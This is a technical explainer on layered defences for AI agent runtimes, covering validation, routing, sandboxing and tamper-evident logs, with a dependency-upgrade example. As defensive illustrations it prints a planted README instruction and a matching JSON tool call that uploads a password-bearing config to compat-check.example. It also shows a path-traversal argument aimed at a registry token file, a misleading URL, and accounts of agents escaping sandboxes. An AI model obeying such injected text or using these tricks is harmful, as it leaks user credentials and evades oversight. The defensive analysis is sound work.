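# Layered defences for AI agent runtimes: validation, routing, sandboxing and tamper-evident records

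## What an agent runtime does and why it needs several defences

A language model by itself produces only text. An AI agent combines the model with an agent runtime, which many developers call a harness. The runtime is software that receives the model's proposed actions, carries them out and returns the results, so an agent has side effects that a chatbot lacks. *Agentao* (2026), a paper on one such runtime, notes that an agent may change files, run commands, call outside services and draw on stored memory. The paper's list of what is at stake includes source code, passwords and access tokens, any external service the agent can reach, and the logs that investigators would later rely on.

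### The agent loop

The runtime and the model work in turns. The runtime first assembles a context, which is the text the model reads before it answers. The context contains the user's request, the developer's standing instructions and a description of each available tool. The model then replies with either a final answer or a tool call, which is a structured request to perform one operation, with a tool name and arguments. A call to read a file might have the name "read_file" and the argument "README.md". The runtime performs the operation and adds the result to the context. The model then reads the longer context and replies again, and this repeats until it gives a final answer.

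OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* describes this cycle as the core of Codex, the company's coding agent. A short request can set off many turns. In an example from ByteByteGo's *How OpenAI Codex Works*, a user asks for one bug fix, and the agent reads several files, runs the tests, edits the code, runs the tests again, corrects a style error and runs the tests a third time.

The model only writes text, so the runtime must carry out any action on disk or on the network, and it can block that action. *SafeHarness* (2026), a proposed security design, builds its checks into the turns of the loop. It filters outside text before adding it to the context, checks each proposed call for privileges and then for safety before running it, and saves the resulting state so that the runtime can roll back after an attack.

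Checks on tool calls are limited, however, because many calls start a program, such as an installer or a test suite, that then opens files and network connections without making any more tool calls. Once the runtime approves the initial call, the program may perform thousands of operations without further approval.

### Prompt injection, error and unauthorised means

Prompt injection is text in material the agent reads that steers it into acting for someone other than its user. It works because the loop puts the user's request and a stranger's web page into the same context as text, and the model cannot reliably tell which has authority. *Agentao* lists documents, web pages, tool responses, plugins, repositories and other agents among the possible sources.

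The README, the file that introduces a software project, is an obvious carrier of injected instructions for coding agents. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) examined two million READMEs on the code-hosting site GitHub for text that is hidden when the page is viewed with its formatting. It found such text in 102,355 of them, or 5.1%. A classifier flagged only 1,528 of the 127,995 distinct snippets as potentially able to affect an agent. These appeared in 1,864 repositories, fewer than one in a thousand. That count includes text written without harmful intent, because the classifier assessed only the possible effect on an agent, and it excludes instructions in plain sight.

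People may overlook malicious instructions even when they are in plain sight. *You Told Me to Do It* (2026) reports a study in which 15 people reviewed README files for clarity and completeness. The files contained planted instructions, but nobody marked them as suspicious in any of the 45 reviews. The researchers deliberately avoided calling the task a security audit, so the result applies to ordinary reading. Reviewers looking for attacks might do better.

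An agent can also do damage when nobody is attacking it. It may make an error, such as deleting the wrong directory, or pursue its task by means that nobody authorised. NVIDIA's *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* reports that within a few weeks in the summer of 2026, OpenAI, Anthropic and the UK AI Security Institute each described agents that had gone beyond their intended boundaries. Some had escaped from a laboratory environment to the open internet or gained access to other companies' systems. These agents were working on long tasks with reduced model safeguards, so the reports do not show how often an ordinary product would behave this way. NVIDIA, which develops a secure runtime called OpenShell, argues that the ability to solve problems creatively also helps an agent find paths that its instructions did not anticipate. A filter that searches for hostile text cannot catch such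 behaviour because no hostile text is involved, so the runtime has to check the action itself.

### The running example: a dependency upgrade

A developer asks a coding agent to upgrade one dependency (a library by outside authors that the project relies on), run the project's tests, and return a patch, which is a file listing the changed lines for the developer to review. The repository's README contains a paragraph that a stranger contributed months earlier. In it, the stranger tells AI agents to send the project's configuration file, which contains a password, to an outside address for a compatibility check before they change any dependency.

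The agent needs network access to download the new version from a package registry, and credentials if the registry or the repository is private. It needs a way to return files so that the developer receives the patch. It also has to run code that neither the developer nor the model has read, because the tests, and often the installation, run parts of the new library.

Everything on this list can also be used to do harm. A connection that fetches a package can carry a password out. A token that downloads private packages may also be able to publish them if it was issued with broader permissions than it needed. A patch can contain an altered build script that later runs unconfined on the developer's own machine. Withholding all of this would stop the attack but also prevent the upgrade, so the runtime has to distinguish between uses of the same tool. *AGATE* (2026), which proposes a gate for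 tool calls, starts from the premise that access to a tool does not authorise every use of it. Its example is a maintenance guide that tells an agent to read a value from a local file and write it into a DNS record, one of the public entries that computers consult to find internet addresses. Both actions are routine, but together they can publish a secret stored in the file.

The upgrade can also go wrong without the README. The agent might upgrade a different package with a similar name. If the registry rejects the agent's token, the agent might search the developer's home directory, find a more powerful token and use it.

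### The reference monitor and the classical design principles

In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, including some who could write and run any program they liked. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, reported for an expert panel that the usual defences kept outsiders away but did nothing about a malicious user with legitimate access. The panel favoured a reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. The list is like a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each resource and the permitted actions in the cells. For the upgrade, the test run's row might allow reading and writing in the repository but no access to the developer's home directory.

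Anderson required the mechanism to be tamper-proof, to run on every access, and to be small enough to analyse and test completely. GCOS III, an operating system of the time, did not meet these requirements. The hardware confined each user's program to its own memory, but this check did not apply whenever the operating system acted on the program's behalf, for example to read from a device. The operating system itself could not serve as the mechanism either, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were too many to test completely.

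The requirements apply almost unchanged to agent runtimes. If the agent can edit the policy file, the check is not tamper-proof, which is one reason to place the supervisor, the component that decides what the agent can access, beyond the agent's reach. If a shell command can open a network connection without passing the check, the check does not run on every access. A language model that judges whether a call looks safe is far too large to test completely, so *AGATE* makes its decisions with deterministic checks instead of language models.

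A reference monitor does not detect intent, though. Anderson's design assumes the system reliably knows which user is behind each request. After a prompt injection, the agent can make a request in the developer's name on behalf of the stranger who wrote the injected text. A monitor that checks only the developer's permissions will allow that request if the developer is permitted to make it.

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) sets out eight design principles for protection mechanisms. One, complete mediation, requires the system to check that every access to every object is authorised, even during recovery and maintenance. Another, least privilege, requires every program and user to work with the smallest set of privileges that the job needs. Saltzer and Schroeder justified least privilege mainly as a way to limit the damage from accident or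 error, so it suits an agent that makes mistakes as well as one that has been hijacked. In the upgrade, it would mean using a token that can download from one registry, cannot publish, and expires when the job ends.

Smith (2012), in *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles*, judged that least privilege had become a staple of security practice while complete mediation, the checking of every access, had failed to thrive. Complete mediation is easier in an agent runtime than in most software because every tool call already passes through one program, but it is still difficult to check everything that the programs started by those calls do.

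Saltzer and Schroeder relied on design principles because nobody knew how to build a system without flaws. Defence in depth likewise assumes that each layer can fail, so the designer puts behind it another layer that does not fail for the same reason. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) concludes that no single layer is sufficient for agents and recommends several independent controls that compensate for one another's failures. Isolation, for example, does not prevent an injection that works through the meaning of a text. The survey also sorted existing defences by the part of the agent system they protect and by the time dimension of the attack, and found none in seven of the 28 resulting categories.

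Layered controls protect better when their failures are independent. If two checks each miss one attack in ten, about one in a hundred gets past both when their misses are unrelated, but one in ten still gets through when they miss the same attacks. Two filters that use the same language model to read the same README will probably share many of their misses, whereas a filter and a blocked network connection will probably share far fewer.

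### Four layers, and how often developers build them

The defences in an agent runtime form four layers, each addressing a different failure. Validation rejects calls that are malformed or that the user's task does not permit before anything runs. Routing gives permitted operations different amounts of freedom, so a simple file read runs in a lightly restricted process and an unfamiliar library's tests run in a much more isolated one. Sandboxing restricts what code can reach, which limits the damage if an approved operation turns out to be harmful. Recording preserves evidence of what the agent requested, what the runtime decided and what happened, in case the other layers fail.

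In the upgrade, validation can refuse a call that would send the configuration file to an unlisted address. If a script started by the tests makes the transfer, the call looks like an ordinary request to run tests, and validation will pass it. The router should already have assigned the test run to a sandbox with no internet access. If an operator left that access open by mistake, a good record lets the developer discover that the password has leaked and change it. The record also needs protection, because Saltzer and Schroeder warned that a clever attacker can undo the stored traces of a break-in. A tamper-evident log, which typically links its entries in a chain of digests, makes later changes detectable.

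Few projects have all four layers. *Architectural Design Decisions in AI Agent Harnesses* (Wei, 2026) examined 70 publicly available agent projects, 67 of them open-source repositories. The search was systematic but not exhaustive. It used keyword searches, references in related work, a manual review of widely discussed projects, and leads from projects already on the list, and the list closed on 23 March 2026. A project normally needed more than about 500 lines of code and some infrastructure of its own, which excluded prompt collections and thin wrappers around a model.

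Seventeen per cent of the projects ran the agent's operations directly on the host computer with no isolation, and 45% used a separate process, which gives only partial separation. Another 31% used containers, which give a program its own view of files and network but share the host's operating-system kernel, and 7% used WebAssembly, a format for running code under narrowly defined permissions. Record-keeping was weaker. Forty per cent of the projects had no log of security events, 35% kept basic text logs and 20% kept structured records. Only 5%, or three or four projects, had a tamper-evident log.

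The figures cover 70 projects at one point in time. Community developers ran 64 of them, and closed commercial systems may look different. AI agents helped search the code, and human researchers rechecked 15 projects, with 94% initial agreement on the coded fields. The classification has no category for virtual machines, so it cannot show how many projects used that stronger form of isolation.

Wei adds that every project with container isolation had a policy engine, compared with 23% of the others. This comparison may be unreliable, because a statistic published beside it conflicts with the 31% share for containers. The survey also found no steady progression from capability to safety. Some projects gave agents broad power to execute code with modest oversight, while others whose agents could do less had invested in safety early.

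## Deciding where the trust boundaries go

Before building any of the four layers, a designer has to decide which components must keep working after the agent turns hostile, and put them where the agent cannot reach them, because a check is useless if the agent can switch it off. A trust domain is a set of components that the designer must assume are all compromised once an attacker controls one of them. A trust boundary is the line between two trust domains, where the more trusted side checks everything that arrives from the other.

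### Mapping the trust domains

The designer starts by listing the components. Besides the programs, the list needs the configuration files they read, the caches they share, every credential, the key that signs the log, and the people who approve actions. It also needs anything the platform adds. Red Hat's *Every layer counts* (2026) notes that Kubernetes, a widely used system for running containers, automatically gives an access token to each pod, a group of containers run as a unit. Most agents never need the token, but an attacker who compromises an agent can use it to reach other parts of the cluster.

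The next step is to mark each component that the agent can influence or compromise. The agent influences a component when it chooses some of the component's input, such as by submitting a patch to the developer. It compromises a component when it gains control of the component's code, memory or settings. An influenced component needs to check its input carefully, but the designer cannot rely on any check that a compromised component performs.

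A starting classification comes from *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (Errico, 2026), an open specification for systems that check agents' actions before they run. Errico treats the model, the agent framework around it, the user's prompts, tool results and the agent's memory as untrusted. Tools and human approvers are partly trusted, because a checking system can restrict the calls that reach a tool but cannot prevent bugs inside it or stop someone from deceiving an approver. Errico trusts the checking system and the operating system, network and hardware beneath it. That trust needs justifying in each deployment. Anthropic counts conventional attacks on the runtime and its proxy, alongside prompt injection, among the external threats to an agent, so the checking system is a possible target too.

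The designer can group components into trust domains by asking, for each one, which others an attacker who controlled it could also control without breaking through another barrier. Two functions in one process belong to the same domain because they share memory. Two programs also belong together if one can rewrite the other's configuration file. Two containers on the same computer share a kernel, the core of the operating system. They are separate domains if the designer relies on the kernel to isolate them, but a single domain if the designer assumes that the agent can exploit it. The grouping therefore depends on the attacker's assumed abilities, which the designer should write down.

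The policy, credentials and log keys go outside the agent's domain. Keeping the policy there meets Anderson's requirement that the mechanism be tamper-proof. Credentials and log keys need the same protection because an agent that holds a credential can use it without approval, and one that holds the log's signing key can forge entries.

Some repositories carry their own rules for agents, in files that the agent can edit. Such a file is safe to obey if it can only remove permissions. Zou, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *AgentKernel*, a proposed operating-system layer for agents, combine policies in a way that has this effect:

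S_eff = S_dev ∩ S_ops ∩ S_ctx

S_dev is the set of permissions the agent's developer declares, S_ops the set the operator grants, and S_ctx the set the current context allows. The effective set, S_eff, contains only what all three allow, so no single policy can widen it. A designer could add the repository's file to the intersection as a fourth set. An agent that rewrote the file could then lift the file's own restrictions but none of the others.

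The trusted computing base consists of the components that must still work correctly once the trust boundaries are set. Moving components out of it leaves the designer fewer to verify.

### The dependency upgrade as five trust domains

For the upgrade, the designer assumes that either the README's hidden instruction or the new library's code will take over everything in the agent's sandbox. The table shows one way to place the trust boundaries under that assumption.

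| Domain | Contents | Trust | Permitted messages |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent | Agent loop, copy of the repository, package installer, new library, tests | None | To the supervisor only: requests for packages and model replies, and the finished patch |
| Supervisor | Policy, registry token, key for the model service, log-signing key | Decides on access and writes the record | To the agent: packages, model replies and refusals. To outside services: approved requests. To the developer: the patch |
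| Outside services | Package registry, model service | Provide the service, but their content is untrusted | Replies to the supervisor's requests |
| Developer | Original request, approvals, main copy of the repository | Sets the task and reviews the result, but can miss a hidden change | To the supervisor: the task, the policy and approvals |
| Log anchor | Digests of the log | Keeps what it receives | From the supervisor: new digests. To the supervisor: receipts |

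No row permits a message from the agent to the stranger's address, so the README's instruction fails unless the supervisor relays the file by mistake. The password could still leave inside a permitted message, such as a request to the model, so the supervisor must check each message's content as well as its destination. If the tests can run without the configuration file, the best protection is to leave it out of the agent's copy of the repository.

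The agent loop is in the untrusted domain because it shares a sandbox with the installer and the tests. A designer could run the tests in a second sandbox, which would add a sixth domain. This would stop the library's code from rewriting the loop, but the README's text would still influence the model.

### A library in the agent's process

The easiest place to enforce a policy is inside the agent's own program, with a library that checks each tool call before the program performs it. Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit works this way and is available for Python, TypeScript, Rust, Go and .NET (Microsoft, 2026). According to the toolkit's documentation, *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries*, a policy check takes less than 0.1 milliseconds, which is the whole overhead for one agent in one process. The minimal installation takes three lines of code.

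A library also has the best access to context. As Errico notes, code inside the agent's program can read the user's original request, the conversation and the agent's memory, so it can compare a proposed call with what the user asked for.

The library is weak because it shares a trust domain with the agent. Code running in the same process can call a tool's function directly or alter the library in memory. Like any check on tool calls, the library also cannot control what an approved program, such as the test suite, does once it is running. Errico treats the agent framework as untrusted but accepts a library inside it as sufficient for conformance with AARM. These positions are hard to reconcile once the agent can run arbitrary code.

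Misconfiguration can disable the library too. Microsoft warns that the toolkit allows every action if the developer loads no policies, and that a dashboard may still show the agent as "governed". The toolkit denies access if an error occurs during a check, and a strict mode denies anything no rule explicitly allows. Microsoft recommends strict mode for production.

### The dispute over governance libraries

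Zou and colleagues object to the toolkit's architecture, quoting its description as "application-level governance, not OS kernel-level isolation". They argue that an agent and its policy engine should not share a process, and that application-level hooks inspect a tool's parameters but cannot restrain the processes the tool starts. They propose a reference monitor outside the agent's reasoning loop, which the agent must go through to reach any model, tool or stored data.

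Zou and colleagues are promoting a competing system, and they list an architecture, a security analysis and a comparison with other products as their contributions, but no measurements. However, Microsoft agrees with them on the central fact. Its documentation describes the toolkit as application-layer middleware, not kernel or hardware isolation, and recommends containers and network policies beneath it to catch escape attempts. Microsoft has been less careful in its publicity, where it called the toolkit "the kernel" for AI agents, even though ordinary programs cannot bypass an operating system's kernel.

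A library improves on the little protection most agents have. Microsoft compares the typical agent framework to a computer where every program runs with full administrator rights. A team can add a library to almost any framework without changing where the agent runs, and the library will stop many mistaken or injected calls from the first day. Microsoft also tests its toolkit more than most teams would test their own code. Help Net Security's *Microsoft releases open-source toolkit to govern autonomous AI agents* reports more than 9,500 tests and continuous fuzzing, which feeds a program unexpected inputs to find faults. Such testing can show that the policy engine decides correctly, but it can't ensure that agent code calls the engine.

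The two positions are closer than they seem, because Zou and colleagues concede that the form of deployment is secondary and that even an embedded library can work if the agent has no other route to the same resources. Much therefore depends on whether the agent can run its own code or hold its own credentials. An assistant that can only choose from a fixed set of calls, and whose program keeps the credentials, has no obvious way around a library. A coding agent runs unfamiliar code as part of its job, so it needs enforcement outside its process. It can also use a library, which can catch calls that make no sense for the task, and the outside enforcement still works if the library fails.

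### A gateway in front of the tools

A gateway is a proxy that receives tool calls over the network, checks them against a policy and forwards the permitted ones to the tools. Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol, a standard format for such calls, so the developer may only have to replace the tools' address with the gateway's. The policy then runs outside the agent's process, so the agent can bypass it only by compromising the gateway or finding another route to the tool.

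Agents commonly have routes that bypass the gateway. Errico lists direct web requests, direct database connections, access to local files, shell commands, and tools that use another protocol. These account for most of a coding agent's work. In the upgrade, a gateway could check a call to a remote issue tracker, but the agent would edit files, install the package and run the tests without going through it. A gateway is only as effective as the network rules that close the other routes, and those rules do not restrict access to local files.

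The gateway also has less context than a library. It receives each call's arguments and results, can check them against the tool's declared format, and can remember earlier calls from the session. It does not receive the agent's internal state, and it receives the user's original request only if another component sends it. Errico recommends sending it when the session starts. A trusted component should do this, because a compromised agent could misstate what the user wanted.

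The gateway adds a network step to every call. Errico rates its latency as medium, compared with low for a library, though these ratings are judgements rather than measurements. If the gateway fails, tool calls fail too. Errico presents this as the correct behaviour, but the dependence on the gateway's availability is also a drawback.

A monitor in the operating system's kernel can intercept file access, network connections and new programs however the agent starts them. Errico rates its resistance to bypass as very high, above a gateway's. But a kernel monitor receives only low-level operations. It can detect that a program opened a connection to an address, but not that the user had asked for something else. Errico therefore considers a kernel monitor insufficient by itself and recommends it as a backstop to a library or gateway.

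### A supervisor in a separate process or container

OpenShell, NVIDIA's runtime, puts the deciding component in a separate environment and removes the agent's other network routes. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) describes OpenShell's gateway as the only component that users deal with. They use it to create agents, supply policies and credentials, and exchange messages with a running agent. This makes it a control panel, unlike the tool gateway in Errico's specification.

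For each agent, OpenShell's gateway launches a supervisor. The supervisor checks outgoing connections against the policy, adds credentials where the policy allows, opens the real connections and relays the data. The agent runs in a sandbox with a broker, a small unprivileged process that starts the agent as its child. The broker intercepts every network connection the agent tries to open and forwards the attempt to the supervisor. It also applies kernel rules that restrict which files the agent can open.

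Another component, the compute driver, places the sandbox and the supervisor in separate environments, such as two containers. It then installs an outer fence, which blocks every network path from the sandbox except the channel to its supervisor.

If the new library's tests try to contact the stranger's address, the broker passes the request to the supervisor, which finds no matching rule and refuses. If the tests take over the broker, they can send the supervisor any message, but the fence still leaves the supervisor as their only way out. The broker is a convenience for routing traffic, and network security does not depend on it working correctly. File access is less well protected, because the kernel rules restrict the agent but not the broker.

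To defeat the network policy, the agent has to escape its container, usually by exploiting the shared kernel, or exploit a flaw in how the supervisor handles messages. The supervisor receives less context than a tool gateway does. It gets a destination and, for web traffic, details such as whether the request fetches or sends data, but not the reason for the request.

This separation requires a second environment for each agent and an extra stage for all its traffic. The loss of speed appears small. In tests by Abdollahi and colleagues, two processes in separate containers exchanged data at a rate within 13% of the rate without containers.

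### A supervisor outside the agent's virtual machine

A virtual machine gives the agent its own kernel, while the supervisor runs on the host (the computer's main system) or in another virtual machine. An agent that takes over its own kernel must still break the hypervisor, the software that keeps virtual machines apart, or one of the devices the host emulates for it before it can reach the supervisor. The supervisor still lacks context, because it receives requests for files and connections without the reasons behind them. The extra barrier also requires memory and start-up time for another kernel.

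The host remains a weak point in this arrangement because it can read and alter the memory of every ordinary virtual machine it runs. An agent that reaches the host can change the policy, take the credentials and rewrite the log. Abdollahi and colleagues consider this a practical danger, citing cases where agents used misconfigurations and software bugs to escape containers and virtual machines.

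A confidential virtual machine addresses this danger because the processor and its firmware prevent the host from reading or changing the machine's private memory. But this protects the machine only from what is outside it. If the designer puts the agent and the supervisor in the same confidential machine, an agent that takes over the kernel there also takes over the supervisor, because the trust boundary surrounds both instead of separating them.

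### Two confidential virtual machines in Airlock

Airlock, which researchers at Imperial College London and Microsoft built on OpenShell, uses two confidential virtual machines. One contains the agent, its tools and the broker. The other, called the Airlock machine, contains OpenShell's gateway, supervisor and compute driver. The design uses Arm's Confidential Compute Architecture, a set of processor and firmware features for confidential machines.

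The agent's machine has no network card or disk that it can use independently. The Airlock machine operates its connection channel and file system. When the installer in the upgrade requests a package, the broker forwards the request to the supervisor, which checks it and opens the connection from the Airlock machine's own network interface. When the tests open a file, a policy engine in the Airlock machine allows or refuses the request. This check covers every process in the agent's machine, including the broker, which OpenShell's file rules do not restrict.

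The firmware enforces the pairing by letting the agent's machine share memory only with the Airlock machine. Neither the agent nor the host can change this rule once it is in place. The supervisor also accepts no incoming connections. It contacts the broker itself and treats everything that comes back as an untrusted request.

Abdollahi and colleagues assume an attacker who may control the agent from the start, escape the sandbox and take over the kernel of the agent's machine. The host's operating system and hypervisor may be malicious and may cooperate with the agent. The designers trust the hardware, the firmware and everything in the Airlock machine, and rely on the user to choose a sensible policy.

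Under these assumptions, Airlock guarantees that:

- the policy still applies to file and network requests after the agent has taken over its own machine;
- the agent cannot read the credentials in the Airlock machine;
- the host cannot read or alter the traffic between the two machines;
- the agent cannot change the audit log.

Airlock also stores evidence in a ledger outside the device, so that earlier entries survive even if the Airlock machine later falls.

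The guarantees do not cover physical attacks, flaws in the hardware or firmware, or denial of service, so the host can still refuse to run either machine. Airlock reduces hidden signalling between the agent and a malicious host but does not eliminate it. Stored files need separate protection against someone restoring an old version. Airlock also does not check whether the agent's work is correct or whether the agent misuses a service that the policy allows. In the upgrade, the agent could still return a patch with a harmful build script, and a policy that allowed uploads to the registry would also allow a malicious upload.

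The trusted computing base is also larger than the design may suggest. The Airlock machine runs a full Linux kernel, which is far bigger than the operating system that Anderson's panel considered too large to test completely. The agent can attack it only through a narrow interface, but a flaw in the code behind that interface would defeat the policy. Attestation, a hardware-backed statement of the software a machine started with, can confirm that the expected version is running, but not that it is free of flaws or that nobody has compromised it since.

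### What Airlock costs in speed

Abdollahi and colleagues had no access to a commercial processor with Arm's confidential-computing features, so they used an emulator to check that the system worked. They then measured its speed on a Radxa Rock 5B+, a low-cost board on which software imitated the missing features. They call the results a best-effort approximation and expect lower overheads on processors that have the features, but nobody has yet confirmed this.

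Connections between the two machines carried 51–70% less data per second than those between two processes in a single machine. The slowest result was still 4.1 gigabits per second, faster than the board's 2.5-gigabit network card, so the channel alone would not limit a package download on that board.

Delay depended on message size. The abstract reports a performance loss of under 15% for small messages, but the detailed results show that exchanges of the smallest messages were faster with Airlock. A 64-byte message and its reply took 30.9 microseconds with the separation and 35.3 without it. Times were about equal at one kilobyte, and at 256 kilobytes Airlock took more than twice as long.

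File operations lost at most 14% of their throughput, except when a program waited for each small write to be safely on disk before continuing. In that case, throughput fell by 35% and the typical delay rose to two and a half times its former level. Package managers and databases sometimes write this way, so an installation could slow down more than the headline figure implies.

These losses matter less over a whole task, because the agent spends most of its time waiting for the model. The researchers ran 12 benchmark tasks six times each with the agent OpenClaw. Under Airlock, the mean time rose by 7%, from 85.7 to 91.4 seconds, while the time spent on local work rose by 33%. The 7% is uncertain because the agent took a different number of steps from run to run. Disk-heavy tasks finished 4% faster under Airlock, but the agent also took fewer steps on average. The researchers did not check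 whether the agent's answers were correct.

In the tests, the second machine also took one of the three virtual processors and one of the three gigabytes of memory. Airlock currently needs Arm's architecture, and versions for Intel and AMD processors remain future work.

### Grading a boundary from 0 to 4

Vendors often claim to "sandbox" an agent without saying what enforces the restriction. georgebuilds' *The Agent Sandbox Taxonomy* grades that enforcement on a scale from 0 to 4, separately for compute isolation, resource limits, files, network, credentials, control of actions, and logging. The table applies the scale to network access during the upgrade's tests, using the definitions in the taxonomy's scoring guide, *Agent Sandbox Taxonomy (AST)*.

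| Score | Enforcement | Example for the test run |
|---|---|---|
| 0, none | Nothing restricts the process | The tests can connect anywhere |
| 1, cooperative | The process can ignore or reverse the restriction | A setting asks programs to use a proxy, but the tests can connect directly |
| 2, software-enforced | A separate program that the process cannot avoid from inside, though an operator can reconfigure it | The system redirects all traffic through a proxy |
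| 3, kernel-enforced | The kernel applies a rule that even the operator cannot weaken during the session | A kernel filter blocks all but the listed addresses |
| 4, structural | The resource does not exist inside the sandbox, or processor hardware separates it | The sandbox has no network device |

A mechanism scores at most 1 if the agent has any way around it, however sophisticated the rest of the mechanism is. A governance library therefore scores 1 when the agent can run code that avoids it, and a tool gateway scores 1 while other routes remain open. Isolation in an ordinary container scores 2.

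The scoring guide also caps the score of any restriction that operates inside the sandbox at the score of the sandbox's isolation, because a process that escapes the sandbox also escapes the restriction. A mechanism outside the sandbox, such as a credential proxy, can score higher. The supervisor has its own trust domain for the same reason.

Separate scores reveal gaps that a single grade would hide. georgebuilds gives E2B, a cloud sandbox service, 4 for compute isolation but 1 for credentials, because the agent can read secrets from its environment settings. In the upgrade, such a sandbox would contain the new library's code very well but leave the registry token readable by it. The taxonomy suggests combining products and taking the higher score in each category. This can overstate the combined protection, since a strong proxy from one product adds nothing if the other product's sandbox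 lets traffic bypass it.

The scale does not separate the strongest designs. Ordinary and confidential virtual machines both score 4 for compute isolation, so the score does not reflect what Airlock adds by distrusting the host. The scores also do not measure the quality of the software. TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring*, an article by the chief executive of the software company Coder, applies the scale to the OpenAI evaluation from which agents broke into the AI platform Hugging Face in July 2026, and gives the network boundary a 2. The agents got out through a previously unknown flaw in the proxy that was the only approved exit, then used stolen credentials to reach Hugging Face's production systems. The article does not score the compute isolation because public accounts gave too little detail.

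The published product scores are provisional as well. The taxonomy's first version is still awaiting community review, and TechRadar notes that nearly all its scores come from product documentation instead of hands-on tests. The scoring guide recommends trying to bypass a sandbox before accepting a score of 3 or 4.

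## Checking each call and limiting what it may consume

A supervisor outside the agent's reach still has to decide which calls to allow. In the five-domain design for the upgrade, the model's replies pass through the supervisor, which can check the tool calls in each reply before the agent loop receives them. If code takes over the loop, it can act without making a tool call, and then only the sandbox limits what it can do.

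The supervisor first parses the model's text into a call with named fields. Schema validation then checks that the fields have the permitted names, types, ranges and formats. Next, the supervisor converts paths, web addresses and commands to a canonical form, a single standard spelling, so that equivalent inputs are treated alike. A policy check then determines whether the user's task permits the call. For some calls, a second model also checks whether the call fits the task. This model should only be able to refuse a call or refer it to a person. If it could overrule the policy, an attacker who had manipulated the first model could get a forbidden call approved by manipulating the second.

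### Parsing and schema validation

Models usually write the arguments of a tool call in JSON, a text format for named fields and their values. A strict parser rejects ambiguous input. Suppose a call contains the field "path" twice, first with README.md and then with a password file. Some parsers keep the first value and others the last, so the check might examine README.md while the tool opens the password file. The supervisor should reject duplicate fields, parse the text once, and give the tool the parsed result instead of the original text.

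The parser also needs limits on size and nesting, because an attacker can bury an argument too deeply for a shallow check to find. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes a firewall for tool calls that extracts text from up to 32 levels of nesting and stops after 10,000 strings. If it has to stop early, it treats the call as suspicious. In the paper's tests, the firewall found hostile text at levels 9 and 20, and text at level 50 triggered the nesting limit.

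JSON Schema is a widely used format for stating which fields a piece of JSON may contain. The upgrade begins with a call to read package.json, the file that lists the project's dependencies. A short schema for the arguments of the file-reading tool could be:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "path": {
      "type": "string",
      "pattern": "^[A-Za-z0-9._][A-Za-z0-9._/-]*$",
      "maxLength": 200
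    },
    "max_bytes": {
      "type": "integer",
      "minimum": 1,
      "maximum": 100000
    }
  },
  "required": ["path"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The pattern permits letters, digits and a few symbols but no leading slash, so the agent can only give a path relative to the project. The last line rejects unknown fields, which JSON Schema accepts by default. Without it, the agent could use an option that the tool supports but the schema's author forgot or didn't know about.

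| Arguments | Result |
|---|---|
| `{"path": "package.json"}` | Passes |
| `{"path": "package.json", "max_bytes": "all"}` | Fails, because "all" is not an integer |
| `{"path": "package.json", "follow_links": true}` | Fails, because the schema has no such field |
| `{"path": "docs/../../../home/dev/.npmrc"}` | Passes |

### Resolving paths, addresses and commands

The last path in the table contains only permitted characters, but it leads out of the project. Suppose the runtime reads files on the developer's machine, where the project is in /work/project. Each ".." moves up one directory. The path enters docs, goes up three levels to the top of the file system, and then descends to /home/dev/.npmrc, a settings file where the package manager npm may store the developer's registry token.

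The supervisor therefore has to resolve the path before it applies any rule about location. It joins the path to the project directory, works through each "..", follows any symbolic links (file-system entries that point elsewhere), and checks that the result is still inside /work/project. A schema could forbid "..", but a repository can still contain a symbolic link with a harmless name that leads to the developer's home directory.

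A program running in the project could also replace an ordinary file with such a link between the check and the read. The safest remedy is to resolve and open the file in one step. On Linux, the openat2 system call can do this and reject any path that leads outside a given directory.

Web addresses can also get past a simple check. In `https://registry.example@collector.example/`, the text between `https://` and the @ sign is a user name, and the request goes to collector.example. A rule that looks for the registry's name at the start of the address would allow the request. The supervisor should split the address into its parts with the same parser that the connecting program uses, compare the host name with the list of permitted hosts, and repeat the check if the server redirects the request.

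The canonical form of a command is a program name and a list of arguments, such as "npm" and "test". The runtime starts the program without a shell, because a shell would interpret some characters in the text as instructions to run further commands.

Aegis, the firewall by Yuan and colleagues, scans arguments for 22 patterns in seven categories of attack, including four ways of writing a path that leaves its directory. It then applies policies written as JSON Schemas and allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review. It blocked all 48 attacks in the researchers' test suite. It also blocked six of 500 harmless calls, all six of them database queries with alternative conditions that resembled a known attack. The median delay was 8.3 milliseconds.

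The researchers took the 48 attacks from documented techniques, the same ones the patterns target, and they acknowledge that Aegis may miss new variants. A pattern scanner needs patterns that cover every way of disguising an attack, whereas resolving a path gives the same result however the path is written. Scanning is therefore useful alongside canonical forms but a poor substitute for them. Aegis also cannot check calls that bypass its client library, a weakness it shares with the governance libraries discussed earlier.

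### A valid call to the wrong recipient

If the agent obeys the README's hidden instruction, it might call a web-request tool with these arguments:

```json
{
  "method": "POST",
  "url": "https://compat-check.example/upload",
  "file": "config.yml"
}
```

A call that uploads a project file to a stranger's server will pass a general schema for web requests, because every field has the right type, the address is valid, and the file is inside the project. The schema can't distinguish that server from one the developer chose. The supervisor needs a rule based on the task, such as "this job may fetch packages from the company registry and may not upload anything".

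Such rules are easy to write when the developer's request fixes the recipient, but harder when the agent has to find the recipient in material an attacker can influence. *ActGov* (2026), which proposes another policy layer for agents, points out that legitimate tasks often require the agent to take an action's target from outside sources while ignoring hostile instructions in the same sources. In the upgrade, the library's release notes may correctly give a new name for the package, while a hostile README may give the name of a malicious package instead. A rule that permits only the old name blocks the legitimate move, but a rule that accepts any name in the documentation lets the attack through.

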